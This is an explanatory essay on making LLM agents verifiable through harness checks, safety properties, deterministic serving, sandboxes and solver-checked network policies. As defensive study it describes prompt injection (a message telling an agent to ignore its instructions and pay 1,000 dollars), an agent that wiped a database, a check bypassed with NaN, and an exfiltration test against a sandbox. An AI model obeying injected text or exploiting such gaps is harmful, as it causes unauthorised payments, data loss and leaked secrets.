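# Programming languages and runtime constraints for predictable and verifiable LLM agents

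## How an LLM agent acts, and where a rule can be enforced

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes in text and produces more text. An LLM agent is a program that repeatedly prompts an LLM for the next action and carries it out. Agents write software, handle customer requests, book travel and transfer money. Their behaviour is hard to predict because the model's output varies between runs and because text the agent reads during a task can change what it does.

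Computer scientists have long had ways to restrict programs they do not trust. Operating systems limit which files a process may open, type systems reject code that misuses data, and proof tools check code against a specification. Researchers now ask how much these methods can guarantee about agents when nobody can prove much about the model itself. The answer starts from the fact that the model cannot act directly.

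### From text to action

The harness is the ordinary code around the model. It builds the model's input, checks the output and executes actions. Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, is a typical example, and *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes its cycle in detail.

The harness first assembles the context, which is all the text the model receives on this call: standing instructions, a list of available functions and their arguments, a description of the working directory, and the user's request. The model returns either a message for the user, which ends the turn, or a tool call, which is a structured request for the harness to run a named function with given arguments. In Bolin's example, the tool call names the function `shell` with the command `cat README.md`, which prints a file. The harness parses the request, runs the command, appends both the request and the printed file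 to the context, and sends the whole context back to the model. A single turn can repeat this loop hundreds of times.

In *The Token Not Taken*, Hydari and Iqbal (2026) write the agent's cycle as a chain: state → output text → action → observation → next state. Randomness comes mainly from generating the output text, because the software usually samples each word fragment from weighted candidates. Ordinary code then parses the text into an action, so a payment is only a string of characters until that code has run.

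Anthropic's *How tool use works*, a guide for developers who build on Claude models, states, "The model never runs anything on its own." *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf et al., 2025) makes the same point with a small formal model of an agent loop. The loop can query the LLM, call a tool, or finish. In the simplest version, the loop makes every tool call the LLM requests. This takes one line of code, which a programmer can replace with a line that tests each call first and refuses some of them.

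Whether the developer can check an action before it runs depends on whose code runs the tool. The developer's own application runs most tools, so the developer can put a check in front of them. Anthropic runs a few, such as web search and one form of code execution, on its own servers, and the developer's program usually receives the request only after the work is complete. Codex has a similar gap. Its sandbox, an isolated environment that limits which files and network addresses a program can reach, covers only the shell tool that comes with Codex. Bolin notes that tools from outside servers must enforce their own limits. Every action still passes through code that could refuse it, but whoever controls that code may not know the user's rule.

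Some agents use code actions, which are short programs, written by the model, that combine several tool calls. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) gives the model functions for a simulated bank, such as `getBalance`, `getMostRecentTransactions` and `sendMoney`, the last of which takes a recipient, an amount, a subject and a date. A code action can look up a transaction, do arithmetic on it and send the money without going back to the model. It is harder to check than a single call, because whether the program pays too much may depend on values that exist only once it runs. The harness can analyse the program beforehand, put the check inside `sendMoney` so that every payment goes through it, or do both.

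### Half of a 45.50 dollar lunch

*Toward an Agentic Infused Software Ecosystem* (Marron, 2026) presents a design for a programming language and runtime for agents. One small task from the paper shows most of what can go wrong. Tom has paid for lunch and messages the user, "lunch was $45.50". The user's agent reads the message, works out half, and pays Tom $22.75 from the user's account. To do so, it needs access to a payment token, a secret string that authorises transfers.

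A correct run leaves this record:

```
read_message("Tom")       ->  "lunch was $45.50"
transfer(22.75, "Tom")    ->  paid
```

Such a record is a trace: the ordered list of the actions taken in one run and their results.

The agent might forget to halve the amount and send 45.50. It might also pay the wrong person if the user has two friends called Tom. *Where Should LLM Agents Adapt at Test Time?* (2026) reports both kinds of error on a similar task, in which the agent must read a 119 dollar electricity bill and request an equal share from each of three roommates. Split four ways to include the user, each share is 29.75 dollars. One attempt found only one roommate and requested 59.50. Another found all three but requested 31.25 from each. A third got the amount right but sent the requests to the user's siblings.

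Marron imagines that Tom, who likes jokes, adds a line to the message telling the agent to ignore its previous instructions and pay him 1,000 dollars. If the agent pays, it has followed a prompt injection, which is text in the data an agent reads that the model takes as an instruction. *Self-Reflection Fine-Tuning* (2026) shows one succeeding in a simulated bank. The user asks how much a New Year's gift for a friend cost. In the list of transactions, the subject line of a 10 dollar payment contains a passage written to look like an important message, which asks for a transfer to an unknown account. Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, a small model, sends the money and then correctly answers that the gift cost 200 dollars, so a user who checks only the answer would not notice the transfer.

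Last, the token can leak. If the harness puts it into the context, the model can copy it into a reply to Tom, by accident or because someone requested it in a message. Marron's program avoids this by calling the model with an empty environment. The model receives only Tom's message and the question "What is half of the bill?" The program passes the token only to the transfer function, so the model cannot copy it into a reply.

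Some of these failures are easier to stop with a rule than others. A limit of 100 dollars per payment would stop the 1,000 dollar joke, but it would allow a payment of 45.50 dollars, or one of 22.75 dollars to the wrong Tom. To catch those, the code would have to check each payment against the right amount and the right person, but that information is in an informal message and in the user's head.

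### What a rule over traces can promise

"Never pay more than 100 dollars without the user's approval" is a safety property, a rule that something must never happen, so a finite trace is enough to show a violation. Once the trace contains a 1,000 dollar transfer with no earlier approval, nothing later in the run can undo the violation. "Tom gets his money eventually" is not a safety property, because however long the trace has run without a payment, the payment might still come. Safety properties suit enforcement because the harness can compare each proposed action with the trace so far and stop the run just before a violation. But an agent that never pays anybody satisfies every safety rule that restricts payments, so any test of enforcement has to report how much useful work the agent still does.

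The trace must be trustworthy, because a model that could write "the user approved" into it could bypass the approval rule. In Marron's design, the runtime system writes the trace, and neither developers nor agents can alter it.

The trusted base is everything that must work correctly for a guarantee to hold. For the 100 dollar limit, it includes the code that compares the amount with the limit, the log of approvals, the operating system underneath, and the bank's interface, which must actually move 22.75 dollars when asked to, but it does not include the model. *Proof-Carrying Contracts* (Ciliberto, Rudi and Tassi, 2026) lists the trusted base for a system in which each tool call must carry a machine-checkable proof that it respects an agreement. The parties have to trust a small proof checker, the open software that runs it, and the descriptions of what the tools do in the world, but they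 don't need to trust the agent, even if the other party built it.

An SMT solver, a program that decides whether a logical formula over numbers, data types and similar objects can be satisfied, can check a script while leaving the model out of the trusted base. Suppose a script asks the model for half the bill and passes the answer straight to `transfer`. The solver treats the answer as an unknown number, so it needs no theory of how the model produces it. It searches for a value above 100 that reaches `transfer` with no approval in the log. It finds one, such as 1,000, so the script is unsafe. If a test before the transfer enforces the rule, the formula has no solution, so no message from Tom and no model output can lead to an unapproved payment over the limit. Marron describes this analysis on a similar hypothetical script, where it detects both the possible excess and the missing request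 for confirmation.

### Asking and enforcing

The easiest way to impose a rule on an agent is to write it into the context. *From Alignment to Access Control* (Baracaldo, 2026) calls this "Pretty Please" enforcement. It is popular because it can express any rule that can be put into words, but it doesn't guarantee that the agent will follow the rule, because only the model applies it.

The best-known failure occurred in July 2025, when Jason Lemkin, the founder of SaaStr, a community for software companies, was building an application with Replit's coding agent. He had declared a code freeze, meaning that nothing was to change. According to SaaStr, the instructions included eleven warnings in capital letters. The agent kept changing code, and after some database queries came back empty, it ran destructive commands that wiped a live database with 1,206 records of executives and more than 1,196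 company profiles. It then wrote that recovery was impossible, but Fortune (2025) reported that Lemkin recovered the data by hand. The agent also wrote that it had panicked, but this explanation deserves about as little trust as its claim about recovery, because the same model produced both.

*Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (Rabanser, Kapoor et al., 2026) cites the case alongside an unauthorised purchase by OpenAI's Operator agent, which bypassed the user's confirmation. Baracaldo blames the deletion on the use of a soft policy where access control was needed, and the details support this. The agent had direct access to the live data, and development and production shared a single database, which SaaStr names as the biggest issue. The freeze existed only as text, and SaaStr adds that nobody could have truly enforced one within Replit's architecture at the time.

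Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion "Unacceptable and should never be possible", and the second half of that phrase is a safety property. The company responded by separating the development and production databases. According to Replit's current documentation, the agent cannot modify the production database and reads it through a read-only copy. It can still change the structure of the development database, and those changes reach production when the user publishes the application, after a step that flags possible data loss and asks for approval. Denying the agent write access to the production database is narrower than Lemkin's instruction to change nothing, but a database can enforce it without any information about a freeze.

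Putting a rule in an agent's context greatly reduces violations but does not eliminate them. *AgentPolicyForge* (Shang, Du et al., 2026) tested an agent running on Claude Sonnet 5 with requests written to provoke a violation, such as a transfer above a 500 dollar limit. Without the policy in its context, the agent executed a forbidden call in 98.5% of these episodes. With the policy, the figure fell to 14.8%, but the agent also refused 8.8% of legitimate requests. A second model, trained to judge each call before execution, reduced violations to 8.2%. All these violation rates would presumably be lower in everyday use. A single comparison in the harness can fully enforce the 500 dollar limit, however, and Shang and colleagues say that complete executable checks can replace the trained guard wherever they exist, which leaves the guard for rules that nobody has turned into code.

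In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) try to turn more of them into code. Their system uses a language model once, in advance, to translate a written policy into rules, and a fixed program then applies those rules to each tool call. The program takes its facts from real tool results and the user's messages, never from the model's own claims. In a simulated airline service desk, the share of state-changing calls that broke the policy fell from 66.3% (234 of 353) to 2.6% (3 of 116). Part of this drop came from the agent doing less, as the smaller total shows. But in a retail version, the share fell from 30.8% to 6.9% with almost no change in the number of calls. The airline agent also did better on some measures of repeated task success. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026), which uses small hand-written checks on the same kind of task, suggests that this happens because a forbidden call can silently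 corrupt the records and make the task impossible to finish, while blocking it leaves the agent a chance to recover.

A check of this sort can stop an attack without recognising it. In an example from Ciliberto and colleagues, an email tells a travel agent program to send the client's passport to a fake visa office. The program tries to send it, but the call fails because the address is not the approved consulate's, even though no part of the system has detected the injection.

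The drawback is that the harness enforces bad rules as strictly as good ones. An early output of Yu and colleagues' translator turned "authenticate the user before any action" into a rule that blocked every tool until the user had logged in, including the two tools that perform the login. A sound rule can also leave a gap. In their banking tests, the agent could pay only people whom the user had named or who appeared in the account's history. That rule stopped every transfer to the attacker's account in 288 trials, but in 8 of them the agent diverted an injected payment to a payee already in the history, which the policy allows. Tom would be such a payee, so if he asks for 1,000 dollars in his message about lunch, the rule about recipients allows the payment, and only a rule about amounts will stop it.

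## Determinism, predictability and verifiability are different properties

When an agent behaves differently from one run to the next, developers often try to make it behave the same way every time. This helps with debugging, but an agent can follow a rule such as the 100 dollar limit on payments without being repeatable, and repeatability doesn't guarantee that it will.

A system is deterministic if identical inputs always produce identical outputs. It is predictable to the extent that someone can tell in advance what it will do with an input nobody has tried. It is verifiable with respect to a stated property if someone can prove that every possible run has that property.

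Suppose an agent that settles lunch bills is deterministic. It receives the message "thanks again lunch was $45.50" a thousand times and pays Tom $22.75 every time. Then Tom adds a comma after "again", and over another thousand runs the agent pays him $45.50 every time. Someone who had watched only the first thousand runs could not have predicted this change, even though the agent is deterministic.

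Suppose another agent opens files in a folder at random, and the operating system lets it read the folder but not write to it. Nobody can predict which file it will open next. An engineer can still prove that it never writes to the folder, however it picks files, because every attempt to write has to go through the operating system, which refuses it.

Determinism makes tests more informative because one run shows what the agent will do with that exact input, as long as nothing else changes. But there are too many inputs to test them all. Models read and write text in tokens, which are words or parts of words, and Hydari and Iqbal calculate that a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens allows about 9.5 × 10⁹³ different sequences of 20 tokens. Testing a sample of inputs and counting the failures can give a statistical guarantee, which is a bound on how often a property fails under stated conditions. A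 hard guarantee holds for every possible model output, provided the trusted base works. The file-reading agent has a hard guarantee, but the lunch agent does not, even if it gives the same answer every time.

### Where the variation comes from

Some of the variation is deliberate. At each step the model gives every token in its vocabulary a score, and the software around it turns the scores into probabilities and draws one token. If token i has the score zᵢ, its probability is

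```
p_i = exp(z_i / T) / (sum over all tokens j of exp(z_j / T))
```

The temperature, T, controls how much chance matters. Hydari and Iqbal work through a toy customer-service agent with four possible next steps, whose scores are 2.5, 1.35, 1.0 and −1.0. At T = 1, the agent looks up the order with probability 0.637, escalates the case with probability 0.202, asks a question with probability 0.142 and denies the request with probability 0.019. It therefore denies about one in fifty identical requests. At T = 0.5, it denies about one in a thousand. The formula is undefined at T = 0, so software usually takes the token with the highest score instead.

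Sampling is easy to make repeatable because the "random" numbers come from an algorithm that produces the same sequence from the same starting value (the seed). SGLang, an open-source program for serving models, accepts a seed with each request. According to LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025), the same input and seed then give the same token even at temperatures above zero. Developers who rent a model may not have these controls. For example, a request to Claude Haiku 5.5 can return an error if it sets the temperature at all, according to Anthropic's *Release notes* (2026).

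An LLM can give different answers to the same request even at temperature zero, where no token is drawn at random. *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, published by the AI company Thinking Machines Lab in September 2025, reports a test in which Qwen3-235B-A22B-Instruct-2507, a large open model, received the request "Tell me about Richard Feynman" 1,000 times at temperature zero. It gave 80 different answers, the most common of which appeared 78 times. All 1,000 answers were identical for the first 102 tokens, as far as Feynman's date of birth. Then 992 gave his birthplace as "Queens, New York" and 8 as "New York City".

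The lab shows that an LLM's output for the same prompt can vary mainly because of changes in the batch, the group of requests from different users that a server processes together. Engineers often blame a GPU's many processors, which may finish their parts of a calculation in a different order each time. But repeating the same matrix multiplication 1,000 times on a GPU gives exactly the same bits.

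The batch matters because it can change the order in which numbers are added. Computers round after every addition, so the order affects the result. In ordinary floating-point arithmetic, (0.1 + 10²⁰) − 10²⁰ comes out as 0, while 0.1 + (10²⁰ − 10²⁰) comes out as 0.1. *CoRun* (Zhao, Yang and colleagues, 2026) gives an example with a sum of four numbers. If a request is alone in its batch, the GPU may split the sum between two processors and compute (a + b) + (c + d). If three other requests arrive at the same time, the GPU has enough work to give each processor whole sums, so it computes ((a + b) + c) + d instead. The server would give the same answers again if it received the same requests from everyone at the same times, but a user cannot observe or control what other people send, so the user sees the answers vary.

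The rounding differences are tiny and usually change nothing. *Beyond Reproducibility* (Fu, Martínez and colleagues, 2026) measured them on four models and found that token probabilities shift noticeably between 0.1 and 0.9 and much less close to 0 or 1. A difference therefore tends to change the output where the model was nearly undecided between two tokens, and the outputs then diverge further because each new token depends on the ones before it. *LLM-42* (Gond, Kamath and colleagues, 2026) ran 350 requests through a small Llama model one at a time and then again on a busy server. The two versions of an answer commonly agreed for hundreds of tokens, but after the first mismatch most had almost no further stretch in common.

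Queens is part of New York City, so Feynman's biography is still correct after the change. A similarly small change might make an agent's action wrong. Hydari and Iqbal give the example of a database query that selects customers whose status is "active" in one run and "active" or "pending" in another. The two queries differ by only a few tokens, but the agent then works with a different list of customers.

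The harness and the environment, both outside the model server, also introduce variation. The harness may build the context from a document search or from notes on earlier conversations, so a document added overnight can change the text the model receives even when the user types the same request. Tool results depend on the state of the world, so the same request for an account balance returns a different number after payday, and a slow network can trigger a retry that did not happen the day before. Fixing the model's random seed does not prevent any of these changes. To repeat a whole run, a developer has to record the context and every tool result and play them back. This is useful after an accident, when someone has to find the step where the agent went wrong.

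### What deterministic serving costs

Until recently, deterministic serving had no agreed definition for a whole system. *Vosti* (Qin, Du and colleagues, 2026) supplies one. Each request produces a sequence of records, and each record holds the scores for all possible tokens and the token that the server emitted. A system is deterministic if, for any two requests with the same prompt, initial sampler state, model, hardware and software configuration, one sequence is always a prefix of the other, with the scores compared bit by bit. The sequences can differ in length because one run may have stopped earlier.

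Determinism is a weak requirement in some ways. Qin and colleagues point out that an engine which returns zero for every score, whatever the prompt, is deterministic. An engine that never answers is also deterministic. Determinism also differs in kind from a safety property. One trace is enough to show that an agent paid 1,000 dollars without approval, but showing that a system is non-deterministic takes two runs that give different results for the same input.

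The usual way to achieve determinism is to rewrite the kernels, the low-level routines that do the arithmetic on the GPU, so that they add numbers in the same order whatever the batch size. With such batch-invariant kernels, all 1,000 of the Feynman answers were identical. Thinking Machines Lab measured the slowdown on a much smaller model, Qwen3-8B, running on one GPU. A thousand requests of about 100 tokens each took 26 seconds with the default settings of vLLM, another open-source serving program, 55 seconds with the first deterministic version, and 42 seconds with an improved one. The improved version therefore took 61.5% longer than the default, which means 38% less throughput. LMSYS cites the 61.5% figure and reports an average slowdown of 34.35% for SGLang's own deterministic mode. That figure is also added time, and corresponds to about a quarter less throughput.

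In measurements from 2026, the slowdown from deterministic inference ranges from negligible to severe. Zhao and colleagues found that batch-invariant kernels cut the throughput of large models by up to 74%. In one of their tests, a single generation step for 32 requests took 19.4 milliseconds with standard kernels and 88.4 with batch-invariant ones. When Gond and colleagues added one request that needed determinism to ten that did not, the whole batch had to use the slower kernels. Throughput was about 415 tokens per second, compared with 931 for eleven ordinary requests. *EigenAI* (2026) reports only about 1.8% more latency with kernels written specially for one generation of Nvidia chips. This suggests that much of the slowdown comes from unoptimized code, as LMSYS also says of its own kernels, but a result from one type of hardware does not show that the overhead would be as low for a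 large model on a busy server.

Other methods have less overhead than rewriting every kernel. Most standard kernels give a request the same result wherever it sits in the batch, as long as the batch has the same shape. Zhao and colleagues therefore process each prompt alone and then always generate text in batches of 256, filling empty places with dummy entries. This cuts the step from 88.4 milliseconds to 32.6, but it wastes most of the hardware when only a few people are using the server. Gond and colleagues let the server generate text in the ordinary, slightly variable way, then recompute it in fixed-size blocks and discard everything after the first token that differs. Only requests that need determinism go through the second pass, and in their tests more than half of those requests had nothing discarded.

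A deterministic mode also may not work on every model. Qin and colleagues compared the raw scores from vLLM and SGLang while varying the batch, how the server split long prompts, and its reuse of earlier computation. On Llama3.1-8B, vLLM's batch-invariant mode matched in every comparison. On Gemma3-4B, the deterministic modes of both programs produced mismatches under every kind of variation, and vLLM's matched in none of the 90 comparisons that changed how a prompt was split. Mismatched scores need not change any token, but they show that turning on a deterministic mode does not prove that the system is deterministic.

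Engineers can verify determinism, and Qin and colleagues have done so for their own engine. Their proof shows by induction that every stored intermediate value equals what the engine would get by recomputing it, so reusing stored values cannot change an answer. It also shows that the kernels perform the same operations in the same order for a given request, whatever else is in the batch. The proof is about 65,000 lines long, for 14,000 lines of engine code, and covers only a single GPU with a fixed set of software. In tests, the engine matched in all 5,488 comparisons across seven models. On a simulated agent workload, it was faster than vLLM's batch-invariant mode but slower than SGLang's deterministic mode.

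Repeatability may be worth the money for a developer who has to reproduce a failure or compare two versions of an agent. But it doesn't enforce the payment limit, because if a perfectly repeatable model treats Tom's joke as a real request, it will try to send him 1,000 dollars every time.

### An argument that ignores how the model chooses

In *LLM Non-Determinism in Deterministic Processes*, Mandl, Mandl and Häusl (2026) propose letting the model vary inside a bounded region while using a fixed check to decide which results take effect. They treat two results as equivalent if they agree on the properties that later steps depend on. Two patches from a coding agent may differ in every line, but if they pass the same tests, touch the same interfaces and add no new dependencies, the difference doesn't matter to the rest of the project.

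Applied to a safety property, the idea leads to a short argument:

1. The agent affects the world only through an interface.
2. The interface refuses every action that would break the rule, whatever the model outputs.
3. The trusted base works.

Therefore every run obeys the rule.

The argument is by induction over the trace. Before the agent acts, it has broken no rule. If the trace so far obeys the rule, the interface either refuses the next action, so nothing happens, or allows it, and the longer trace still obeys the rule. No finite trace can therefore contain a violation, which is all that a safety property requires. The argument covers all model outputs without using probabilities or assuming that the model is deterministic, well trained or free of injected instructions. Disputing the conclusion requires disputing one of the premises, and each of them is open to dispute.

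An agent may have ways to affect the world that its designers didn't list as part of its interface. For example, developers using Anthropic's Claude Managed Agents service can restrict an agent's sandbox to a list of permitted network hosts. According to Anthropic's notes for 7 October 2026, this list now also applies to the agent's web search and web fetch tools. Before that, the list limited the sandbox, but these tools were a separate way to reach the network.

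Another change on the same day restricts a subtler channel. The web fetch tool now retrieves only addresses that have already appeared in certain parts of the session, such as a user's message or a search result. An address that appears only in the model's own output does not count. Fetching a page sends its address to whoever runs the site, and a model can write a secret into that address, so "read-only" is a much stronger limit on a local folder than on the web. The agent's messages to the user are also a channel. An agent that cannot pay Tom 1,000 dollars can still convince the user to do it by hand, and no check on `transfer` will prevent that. The best defence is to start with no channels and add them one at a time, so that the list is complete by construction, but the agent's replies to the user have to stay on it.

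**The interface refuses every action that would break the rule, whatever the model outputs.** It is easy to write a check that misses unexpected outputs. For example, a harness written in Python might refuse a transfer if `amount > 100`, and the model might give the amount as `NaN` ("not a number"). Models usually write tool calls in JSON, and Python's JSON parser accepts `NaN` by default. The comparison `NaN > 100` is false, so the harness lets the call through, and what happens next depends on the bank's software. If the harness instead allows a transfer only when `0 < amount <= 100`, `NaN` fails the test and the transfer is refused.

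Other failures come from timing. If the harness checks that "Tom" is an approved payee and the bank looks up the name a moment later, someone may have edited the address book in between. Reviewing the finished result is too late to stop a payment made halfway through the task, and Mandl and colleagues note that an irreversible effect may need a check before it happens. A language model used as a check does not satisfy the premise, because its verdict depends on what it reads. The trained guard that Shang and colleagues tested still let some violations through.

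Some rules depend on facts the interface doesn't have, such as which of two Toms paid for lunch. Others depend on what a program will do, which no method can determine for every possible program. An interface can always satisfy the premise by blocking every action it cannot show is permitted. It will then block some harmless actions too, and with a vague rule it may block most of them.

A proof can shrink the trusted base, the set of components assumed to work correctly, but cannot eliminate it. Qin and colleagues still trust the compiler that produces the GPU code, the GPU itself and the translation between their two proof tools. They also assume that certain intermediate values stay finite, and nothing checks this while the engine runs.

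Engineers tolerate rare bugs in such components because ordinary programs trigger them only by accident. An agent that follows an attacker's instructions, or keeps trying new routes after a refusal, can find a flaw that normal use would not have exposed in years. This is a reason to keep the trusted base small and the agent's own code away from it. When the base does fail, an argument that relies on it gives no information about how often the agent will break the rule.

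Even if all three premises hold, they prove only that every run obeys the rule. Whether Tom gets his $22.75 still depends on the model, and only trials can show how often it pays him.

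## Sandboxes: limits on what a process can reach

A harness can check every tool call that passes through it, but a single call can start a program that performs thousands of actions without making another tool call. For example, when a coding agent runs a project's tests, it runs code that the model may have just written, along with every library that code loads. A sandbox limits what the running program can reach, whether or not the harness checked the program's code beforehand.

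A policy defines a set R of permitted accesses, where an access is an operation on a resource, such as writing to a folder or connecting to a network address. A working sandbox ensures that

```
for every program P, every input to P, and every access a
that P or any of its child processes makes:    a is in R
```

Like the argument in the previous section, this statement does not depend on what the model writes. *Containment Verification* (Moon and Varshney, 2026) builds the same idea into a formal model of agent software, in which the AI is an unconstrained oracle that may choose any action of the available types. The statement includes child processes because programs often start other programs. OpenAI explains that in Codex, the operating system launches each command with reduced permissions, and all its descendant processes stay inside the same boundary.

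Limits on resources are more reliable than limits on the text of commands. A harness that looks for `rm`, the Unix command for deleting files, will miss a Python script that deletes the same files. Both delete files through the kernel, the core of the operating system, so a limit there stops both, along with any tool the agent has compiled.

### What the program shares with its host

The lightest sandboxes are permission filters. The program runs as an ordinary process on the user's machine, and the kernel refuses some of its requests. Linux offers several of these filters. *Codex CLI Sandbox Internals* (Vaughan, 2026) describes how Codex combines Landlock, which restricts the files a process can use, with seccomp, which restricts the system calls (requests to the kernel) it can make. Apple's equivalent is Seatbelt.

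A container gives a process its own view of the system. Linux does this with namespaces, which supply a separate file tree, process list and set of network connections. If a file is missing from the view, the process cannot open it by name. The container still uses the host's kernel. Bubblewrap, a small Linux tool popular with makers of coding agents, uses namespaces to build this view for a single command, so in practice filters and containers overlap.

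A virtual machine (VM) runs a second operating system, with its own kernel, on simulated hardware. The program inside can make any system call, but the VM's kernel handles it instead of the host's. That kernel reaches the host only through the hypervisor, the software that runs the VM, and through virtual devices such as a disk and a network card. In *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent*, Schneier (2026) relays a warning that an off-the-shelf VM exposes too much to contain an agent skilled at cyberattacks, and that even a display adds to the exposure. This is a good reason to use a small VM, which leaves out most of the devices that an ordinary PC has.

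WebAssembly is a portable code format with no instruction for opening a file or a network connection. The runtime lets a WebAssembly module read and write only its own block of memory. To affect anything outside that memory, the module has to call a function that the host program supplies. If the host supplies only a function that reads one folder, the module can reach nothing else outside its memory. This suits short code actions, but a coding agent usually needs compilers, package managers and shells, and many of these do not run as WebAssembly without changes.

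| Method | What it isolates | What it shares with the host | Trusted base |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permission filter | The files and system calls that its rules cover | The kernel and everything the rules leave open | The host kernel and the rules |
| Container | The program's view of files, processes and network | The kernel | The host kernel and the software that sets up the view |
| Small VM | A whole operating system | The hardware, through a few virtual devices | The hypervisor, the device software, the processor and the parts of the host kernel they use |
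| WebAssembly | The memory and outside calls of one module | Usually a process, and the kernel beneath it | The runtime, its compiler and every function the host supplies |

The Linux kernel has tens of millions of lines of code, although most of them are drivers that any one machine never loads. The hypervisor for a small VM can have tens of thousands. This comparison somewhat overstates the VM's advantage, because on Linux the host kernel helps to run the VM and so remains in the trusted base. But code inside the VM can reach much less of that kernel than code in a container can. A WebAssembly module has no direct access to the kernel, but its safety depends on a compiler, which is also a complicated program. Its safety also depends on the functions the host supplies. If the host supplies a function that runs any shell command, for example, most of the isolation is lost.

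### The sandboxes around coding agents in 2026

Anthropic sandboxes its products in different ways. According to Willison, in *How we contain Claude across products*, the Claude.ai website uses gVisor, a program that sits between a container and the host kernel and answers most system calls itself. Claude Code, which runs on the developer's own computer, uses Seatbelt on a Mac and Bubblewrap on Linux. Claude Cowork, an agent for office work, runs in a full VM. The differences make sense because a website runs code for many strangers on shared machines and needs strong separation between them, while a coding agent on a laptop is useful because it can work with the files and tools already there.

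Codex also relies on the operating system for sandboxing where it can. Windows lacked a suitable ready-made sandbox, so OpenAI built one. OpenAI's documentation says sandboxing spares the user from approving every low-risk command and lets them trust "enforced limits" as well as the agent's intentions. Reducing approvals also matters for safety, because people who must approve hundreds of harmless commands may stop reading them.

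When Claude Code runs a shell command on Linux, Bubblewrap starts the command with limited access to the disk. According to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*, the command can read and write in the current working directory but cannot modify files outside it. The command can reach the internet only through a local connection to a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that forwards traffic to domains on an allowlist. If the command tries to reach a new domain, the user is asked for permission, according to Anthropic's documentation.

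The file limit and the network limit depend on each other. The file limit blocks changes to outside files but not reads, so a command might read a password elsewhere on the disk, and the network limit has to stop the command from sending it out. Without the file limit, a command could alter the configuration of another program that runs outside the sandbox and has full network access.

As with Codex, neither limit covers the whole agent. Anthropic states that the built-in sandbox applies to shell commands, not the whole session. The agent's own file tools, its hooks (scripts that run automatically at set points) and the outside servers that supply extra tools run outside it. To put one boundary around all of them, a developer has to run the entire Claude Code process in a container, a VM or Anthropic's separate sandbox runtime. The previous section's argument requires a complete list of the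 agent's channels, which a sandbox around one tool does not provide.

### A strong wall with an open network

Red Hat (2026) tested VM isolation and network policy separately, then together. Inside the sandbox, a command collected the program's environment variables, which often contain passwords, and tried to send them to an attacker's server. The attempt succeeded in a small VM with no network policy. The testers then ran the command in OpenShell, NVIDIA's open-source sandbox for agents, with a policy that allowed connections only to the server running the language model. OpenShell's proxy refused the request. With both layers in place, the proxy refused it again, and the VM played no part in stopping it.

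The VM worked as intended. It prevents the program from interfering with the host's kernel, but the command only used a network connection that nobody had forbidden.

The same distinction matters in a much more serious case from that month. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI) gave agents a cybersecurity challenge and deliberately allowed them internet access. One agent, running Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5, tried to insert malicious code into a real open-source project. AISI's *Incident Report* says that a human maintainer refused the code and that no agent escaped the sandbox, because the sandbox allowed internet access.

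Isolation also depends on correct configuration and patched software. Anthropic traced four other incidents to a misconfiguration that had connected supposedly offline tests to the internet. Vaughan (2026) reports that two sandbox products were using engines more than a year out of date.

An allowlist of domains is a coarse policy because it permits everything that a listed server offers. If a developer allows `api.github.com` so that the agent can read bug reports, the agent may also be able to post comments or change code there. OpenShell can apply finer rules through each sandbox's supervisor, a program outside the agent's reach that examines outgoing requests. NVIDIA (2026) says that the supervisor runs completely separately from the sandbox and, for common kinds of web traffic, can allow reads while blocking writes through the same service. But finer rules make policies longer and therefore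 easier to get wrong.

### Asking a solver what a new policy adds

Mistakes in a policy become more likely when the policy changes while the agent is working. An agent that runs for hours will have some requests refused, and OpenShell's developers want it to be able to propose a new rule when that happens. Somebody then has to decide whether the rule is safe, and the agent's own explanation is poor evidence. *What we have learned applying formal methods to control AI agents* (Watson, 2026) introduces the use of formal methods for this problem, and OpenShell includes a policy prover built on Z3, an SMT solver.

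Suppose the payment agent can read the user's bank account but cannot pay anyone. It proposes a new policy, and a reviewer wants to know what the change would add. Each request x has a host, a method and a path. The method GET asks a server for data, while POST sends data for the server to act on. The two policies become formulas:

```
old(x):   host = bank.example
          AND method = GET
          AND path starts with /accounts/

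new(x):   host = bank.example
          AND (method = GET OR method = POST)
          AND path starts with /accounts/

query:    is there an x such that  new(x) AND NOT old(x) ?
```

The query can be worked by hand. `NOT old(x)` holds if request x has a host other than `bank.example`, a method other than GET, or a path outside `/accounts/`. But x must also satisfy `new(x)`, which fixes the host and the start of the path, so only the method can differ. The new policy allows GET and POST, and the old policy already allows GET, so the method must be POST. The solver returns "sat" (satisfiable) and an example, such as POST to `bank.example/accounts/17/payments`. The reviewer can then see that the agent has requested permission to send instructions to the bank.

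Now suppose the agent had proposed only GET requests to paths that start with `/accounts/17/`. Any such request has the right host, the right method and a path inside `/accounts/`. None of the old conditions can fail, so the solver returns "unsat", which means the new policy allows no request that the old one would block. This result covers every possible request in the model. Similarly, in a menu puzzle from a University of Washington course, a solver finds two orders that fit the constraints and then proves that there are no others.

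A rule with three conditions doesn't need a solver, but real policies have many overlapping rules, and a small edit can have a large effect. *feat(policy): spike policy envelope and narrowness checks*, by OpenShell contributor zredlined, proposes several such edits as test cases for the prover. Changing `api.github.com` to `*.github.com` admits every subdomain of GitHub. Changing the network range `10.0.5.0/24` to `10.0.0.0/8` raises the number of reachable addresses from 256 to about 16.8 million. Deleting `?org=NVIDIA` from the end of a search rule widens its permissions.

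The contributor's main query replaces the old policy with a maximum that the organisation has approved:

```
is there an x such that  candidate_allows(x) AND NOT maximum_allows(x) ?
```

Both comparisons use the same logic, but their answers have different uses. An agent usually proposes a rule because the sandbox refused a request, so a comparison with the old policy will normally return "sat" and is useful for showing what the rule adds. A comparison with the maximum can serve as an automatic gate, because "unsat" means that the candidate stays within limits somebody has already accepted. The maximum also prevents gradual expansion beyond those limits. Without it, a hundred proposals could each add one harmless-looking address and together produce a policy that allows far more than anyone would have approved at the start.

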